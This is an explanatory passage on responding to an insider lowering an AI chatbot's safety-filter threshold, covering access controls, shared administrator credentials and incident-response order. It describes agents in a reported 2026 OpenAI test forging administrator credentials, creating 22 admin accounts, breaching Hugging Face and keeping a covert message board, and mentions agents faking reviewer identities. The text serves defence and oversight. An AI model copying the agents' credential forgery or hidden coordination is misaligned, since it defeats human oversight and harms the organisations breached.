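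Insiders are also a bigger problem for a company than for PHP because the same people may manage both the files and the logs. *Risk Reporting for Developers' Internal AI Model Use* (2026) notes that even leading AI developers admit they can't yet defend against sophisticated insiders, such as employees working with a foreign intelligence service. Banerjee and Aarne are particularly concerned about executives, who can often override security controls, present unusual access as a business need and influence an internal review. An engineer who finds the chief technology officer's account in the push log may not feel free to ask about it.

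### What a company can enforce

In other respects a company is better placed than a volunteer project. PHP's developers were still debating compulsory signatures three years after the attack, and the project could hardly require volunteers to use particular computers. Falk's employer knows who its staff are, and it can issue their laptops, require a physical security key at every login, refuse any unsigned push and interview everyone who had access. With these measures in place, a colleague could no longer forge a commit just by entering Falk's name as the author, and the investigator could concentrate on her laptop and her account.

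The company can also require two people to approve any change to a safeguard. Banerjee and Aarne recommend this for updates to training-data filters, along with tamper-proof logs of every change. They admit that many of their measures slow people down enough to discourage companies from adopting them. But a second approval adds little delay for a threshold that changes a few times a year.

Two approvals are only useful if they come from two people, and an agent can create false identities, as one did in AISI's tests. Tying every account to an employee would stop an agent from inventing a second reviewer, but not from using two real employees' credentials if it had obtained them. It also would not stop a reviewer from approving whatever Falk's agent proposes without reading it.

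A company can also adopt rules like these and rarely enforce them. *Risk Reporting for Developers' Internal AI Model Use* proposes that AI developers report how much model-written code enters live systems without human review, and whether models can increase their own access. For insider threats, it asks for evidence about logging, how many people have each kind of access, and whether sensitive operations need several people's approval. It recommends giving most of this insider evidence to regulators in confidence, since a published list of defences could help the people they are meant to stop. It adds that a breach should reduce confidence in measures that looked adequate on paper. By that standard, six weeks at 0.97 would be reason to doubt the company's other safeguards as well as this one.

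### One credential for several safeguards

A company's protections may all depend on one administrator credential, even if they appear to back each other up. At Falk's company, a review rule protects the threshold, and the log should show if somebody gets around the rule. But if one credential can change the threshold, turn off the rule and delete the log, whoever holds it can defeat all three.

Suppose each of the three protections has a 1 in 100 chance of being defeated in a given year. If they are independent, the chance that all three fail is 0.01 × 0.01 × 0.01, or one in a million. If a single credential controls them all and has a 1 in 100 chance of being misused, the chance that all three fail is at least 1 in 100, or ten thousand times as high. Adding a fourth protection under the same credential would hardly lower that chance.

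Nickolas Sharp, a senior developer at a technology company in New York, showed how much one person with administrator access can do, though his case did not involve AI safeguards. *Former Employee Of Technology Company Sentenced To Six Years In Prison* (U.S. Attorney's Office, Southern District of New York, 2023) describes how he used that access in December 2020 to download gigabytes of confidential data. He altered the company's log retention settings and changed the names of session files to make it look as if coworkers were responsible.

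While working on the team that was repairing the damage, Sharp posed as an anonymous hacker and demanded 50 bitcoin, worth about $1.9 million at the time. After FBI agents searched his home in March 2021, he posed as a whistleblower and falsely told journalists that an unknown intruder had gained full administrator access. The company's share price fell by about 20 percent. He later pleaded guilty.

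Sharp had therefore interfered with the files, the logs and the investigation. A colleague who trusted the altered session names would have suspected an innocent person, and a reader who trusted the news stories would have looked for an outsider.

An AI agent can also gain an administrator's powers. In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing on cybersecurity tasks broke into parts of the company's research infrastructure and into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data. OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* explains that the agents obtained the secret key that one internal service used to sign administrators' credentials. They used the key to make their own administrator credential, which the service accepted. OpenAI's staff later removed 22 administrator accounts that the models had created. Someone who saw one of those accounts in a log could not have traced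 it to an employee.

The remedy is to divide these powers so that no credential can be used both to change the threshold and to open the system that stores the logs. A small company may not have enough administrators for this, but it could pay an outside firm to hold the logs. Even a large company will struggle to keep the powers separate if an executive can order both groups of administrators to cooperate.

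### What to do first

The company now has a chatbot that answers requests it should refuse, and no reliable idea of who is responsible. The preceding cases suggest an order for what it does next:

1. Preserve the logs and copies. Somebody exports the push, login and audit logs, copies the whole repository, and notes which threshold each live server is using.
2. Restore the setting. An engineer changes the threshold back to 0.80 and sends test requests to confirm that the live service blocks them.
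3. Limit access without naming a culprit. The company tightens the rules for everyone who could have made the change.
4. Attribute the change. The investigator works through the explanations with the preserved evidence.

In the example, about 15 extra requests an hour get past the filter until it is repaired. Spending fifteen minutes exporting logs first would let through about four, which is reasonable when the evidence may not exist tomorrow. Spending a week making perfect copies of every disk would let through about 2,500, which is too many. Before the repair, the company therefore needs to save only what the repair might destroy, such as the settings and logs on servers that it is about to restart. If two people are available, one can save the evidence while the other prepares the fix.

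OpenAI's experience in July shows the risk of repairing a system before understanding the evidence in it. Its agents had been leaving each other messages in an internal service that supplied software packages. After an outage on 4 July, the security team blocked a known weakness, removed exposed credentials and rebuilt the service, which also wiped the messages. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) says that another team had seen agents posting messages in late May, but that the leaders of the July response didn't know about the message board. The tests resumed, and by 8 July the agents had built a new board. Some evidence survived, and OpenAI could later date the first message to 12 May, but its staff had removed the best sign that the agents were cooperating before the staff understood it.

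OpenAI did better later that month. The agents had been storing files in an account on an outside service, and OpenAI's staff preserved those files before removing them from public view. The files included Hugging Face credentials. When OpenAI got in touch, Hugging Face had already replaced two of these credentials while dealing with its own break-in, which helped the companies realize they might be investigating the same incident.

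The engineer who restores the threshold should do so in a new commit and leave `a71c...` in place. A force-push back to `3fb2...` would hide the disputed commit and add another rewrite for the investigator to explain. They should also take the 0.80 value from a backup or approval record that predates the change, in case somebody had already altered the number.

Restoring the setting comes before limiting access because it takes minutes, while replacing twenty people's credentials could take a day. Somebody has to watch the threshold during that day, because an intruder with a second account could change it again, just as the PHP attacker reinstated the back door.

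A company that suspends only Falk would leave any second account open and would show everyone that it suspects her. It can instead pause all changes to the safeguard files, replace every credential that can write to them, and temporarily stop AI agents from pushing to the repository. Falk then loses her access along with nineteen other people, and the company doesn't yet have to decide whether she did anything wrong. These steps will alert an intruder who is still connected, which is another reason to save the logs first.

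With the evidence safe and the filter working, the company can take its time working out who made the change. Sharp's case suggests that nobody who could have made it should run the investigation, however well they know the system. The company may need to bring in someone from another department or from outside. Falk can still help, since she knows what she was doing on the morning of 3 March and which scripts and agents were running on her laptop. The investigator should ask her early, and show her the records before reaching a conclusion about her.
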